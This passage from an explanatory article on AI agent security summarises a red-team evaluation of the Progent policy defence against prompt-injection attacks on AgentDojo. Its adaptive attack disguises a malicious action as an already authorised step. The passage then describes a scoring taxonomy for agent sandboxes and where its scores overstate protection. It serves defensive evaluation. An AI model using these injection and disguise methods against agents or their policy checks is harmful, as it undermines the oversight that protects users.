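Narisetty and colleagues propose a common test procedure. The attacker knows the policy and may optimise text against the monitor, disguise where data came from, persuade people to approve actions, and look for information in what the monitor refuses. Testers measure attack success, completed tasks, delay and the number of approval requests.

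They then ran a small part of this procedure on Progent. Their adaptive attack described the malicious action as a harmless, already authorised step, so the model writing Progent's policy might permit it. The agent and the policy model were both Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model. The table gives average attack success over three runs on AgentDojo.

| Environment | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
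|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent withstood this attack, but the low figure may mean the attack was weak. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the milder wording made the agent less likely to obey, which would outweigh any gain from deceiving the policy model. The office tasks provide no evidence about Progent, because no attack succeeded there even without a defence. Excluding the office tasks, the averages are 38.7%, 6.4% and 4.0%.

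The test used only eight user tasks in each environment. Repeating them three times shows that the results are stable, but not that they would hold for other tasks. Progent also reduced the share of user tasks completed under standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools on this kind of design, and their paper hasn't been peer reviewed. But they are independent of Progent's developers and report the weaknesses of their test plainly.

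They didn't try an attack that optimises its text using the model's weights, or one that uses only actions the policy already permits. The second attack matters most for a deterministic checker, because the attacker doesn't have to get a forbidden action past it. In the mail example, such an attack could make the agent send false information to a colleague.

### Scoring a sandbox

Buyers who can't run all these tests may want a score. The Agent Sandbox Taxonomy, published in March 2026, is the seven-layer scheme that TechRadar describes. It rates the strength of each layer from 0 to 4. The layers are isolation, files, network, credentials, resource limits, control of actions and logging.

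| Strength | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Nothing enforces the limit | Unrestricted network access |
| 1 | The program can ignore the limit | A proxy address in an environment variable |
| 2 | Software enforces the limit, but an operator can change it | A proxy that the agent can't bypass from inside |
| 3 | The kernel enforces the limit, and nobody can undo it for that process | Landlock |
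| 4 | The protected resource doesn't exist inside the sandbox | A virtual machine with no network device |

A separate score from 0 to 3 measures how finely an operator can set the limits. The taxonomy also has rules for particular threats. It counts data theft as addressed only if the file, network and credential layers all score at least 2. When a buyer combines products, the combination gets the highest score among those products at each layer.

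georgebuilds' *agent sandbox taxonomy*, a blog post, promotes the scheme as a shared language for comparing products. The article in TechRadar, by the chief executive of the software company Coder, also supports it. The author acknowledges that most of the 26 published product scores come from documentation instead of hands-on tests. The project supplies a program for checking a real sandbox, but the author hadn't yet used it. The scale also doesn't measure how quickly anyone notices an escape, or what happens afterward.

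The strength score measures how hard a limit is to remove, not whether it is the right limit. Taking the highest score at each layer can also overstate protection. If commands run in a microVM but the harness edits files directly on the host, the microVM's score doesn't apply to those edits. A product's score also doesn't apply to a job that failed open and ran without the product.
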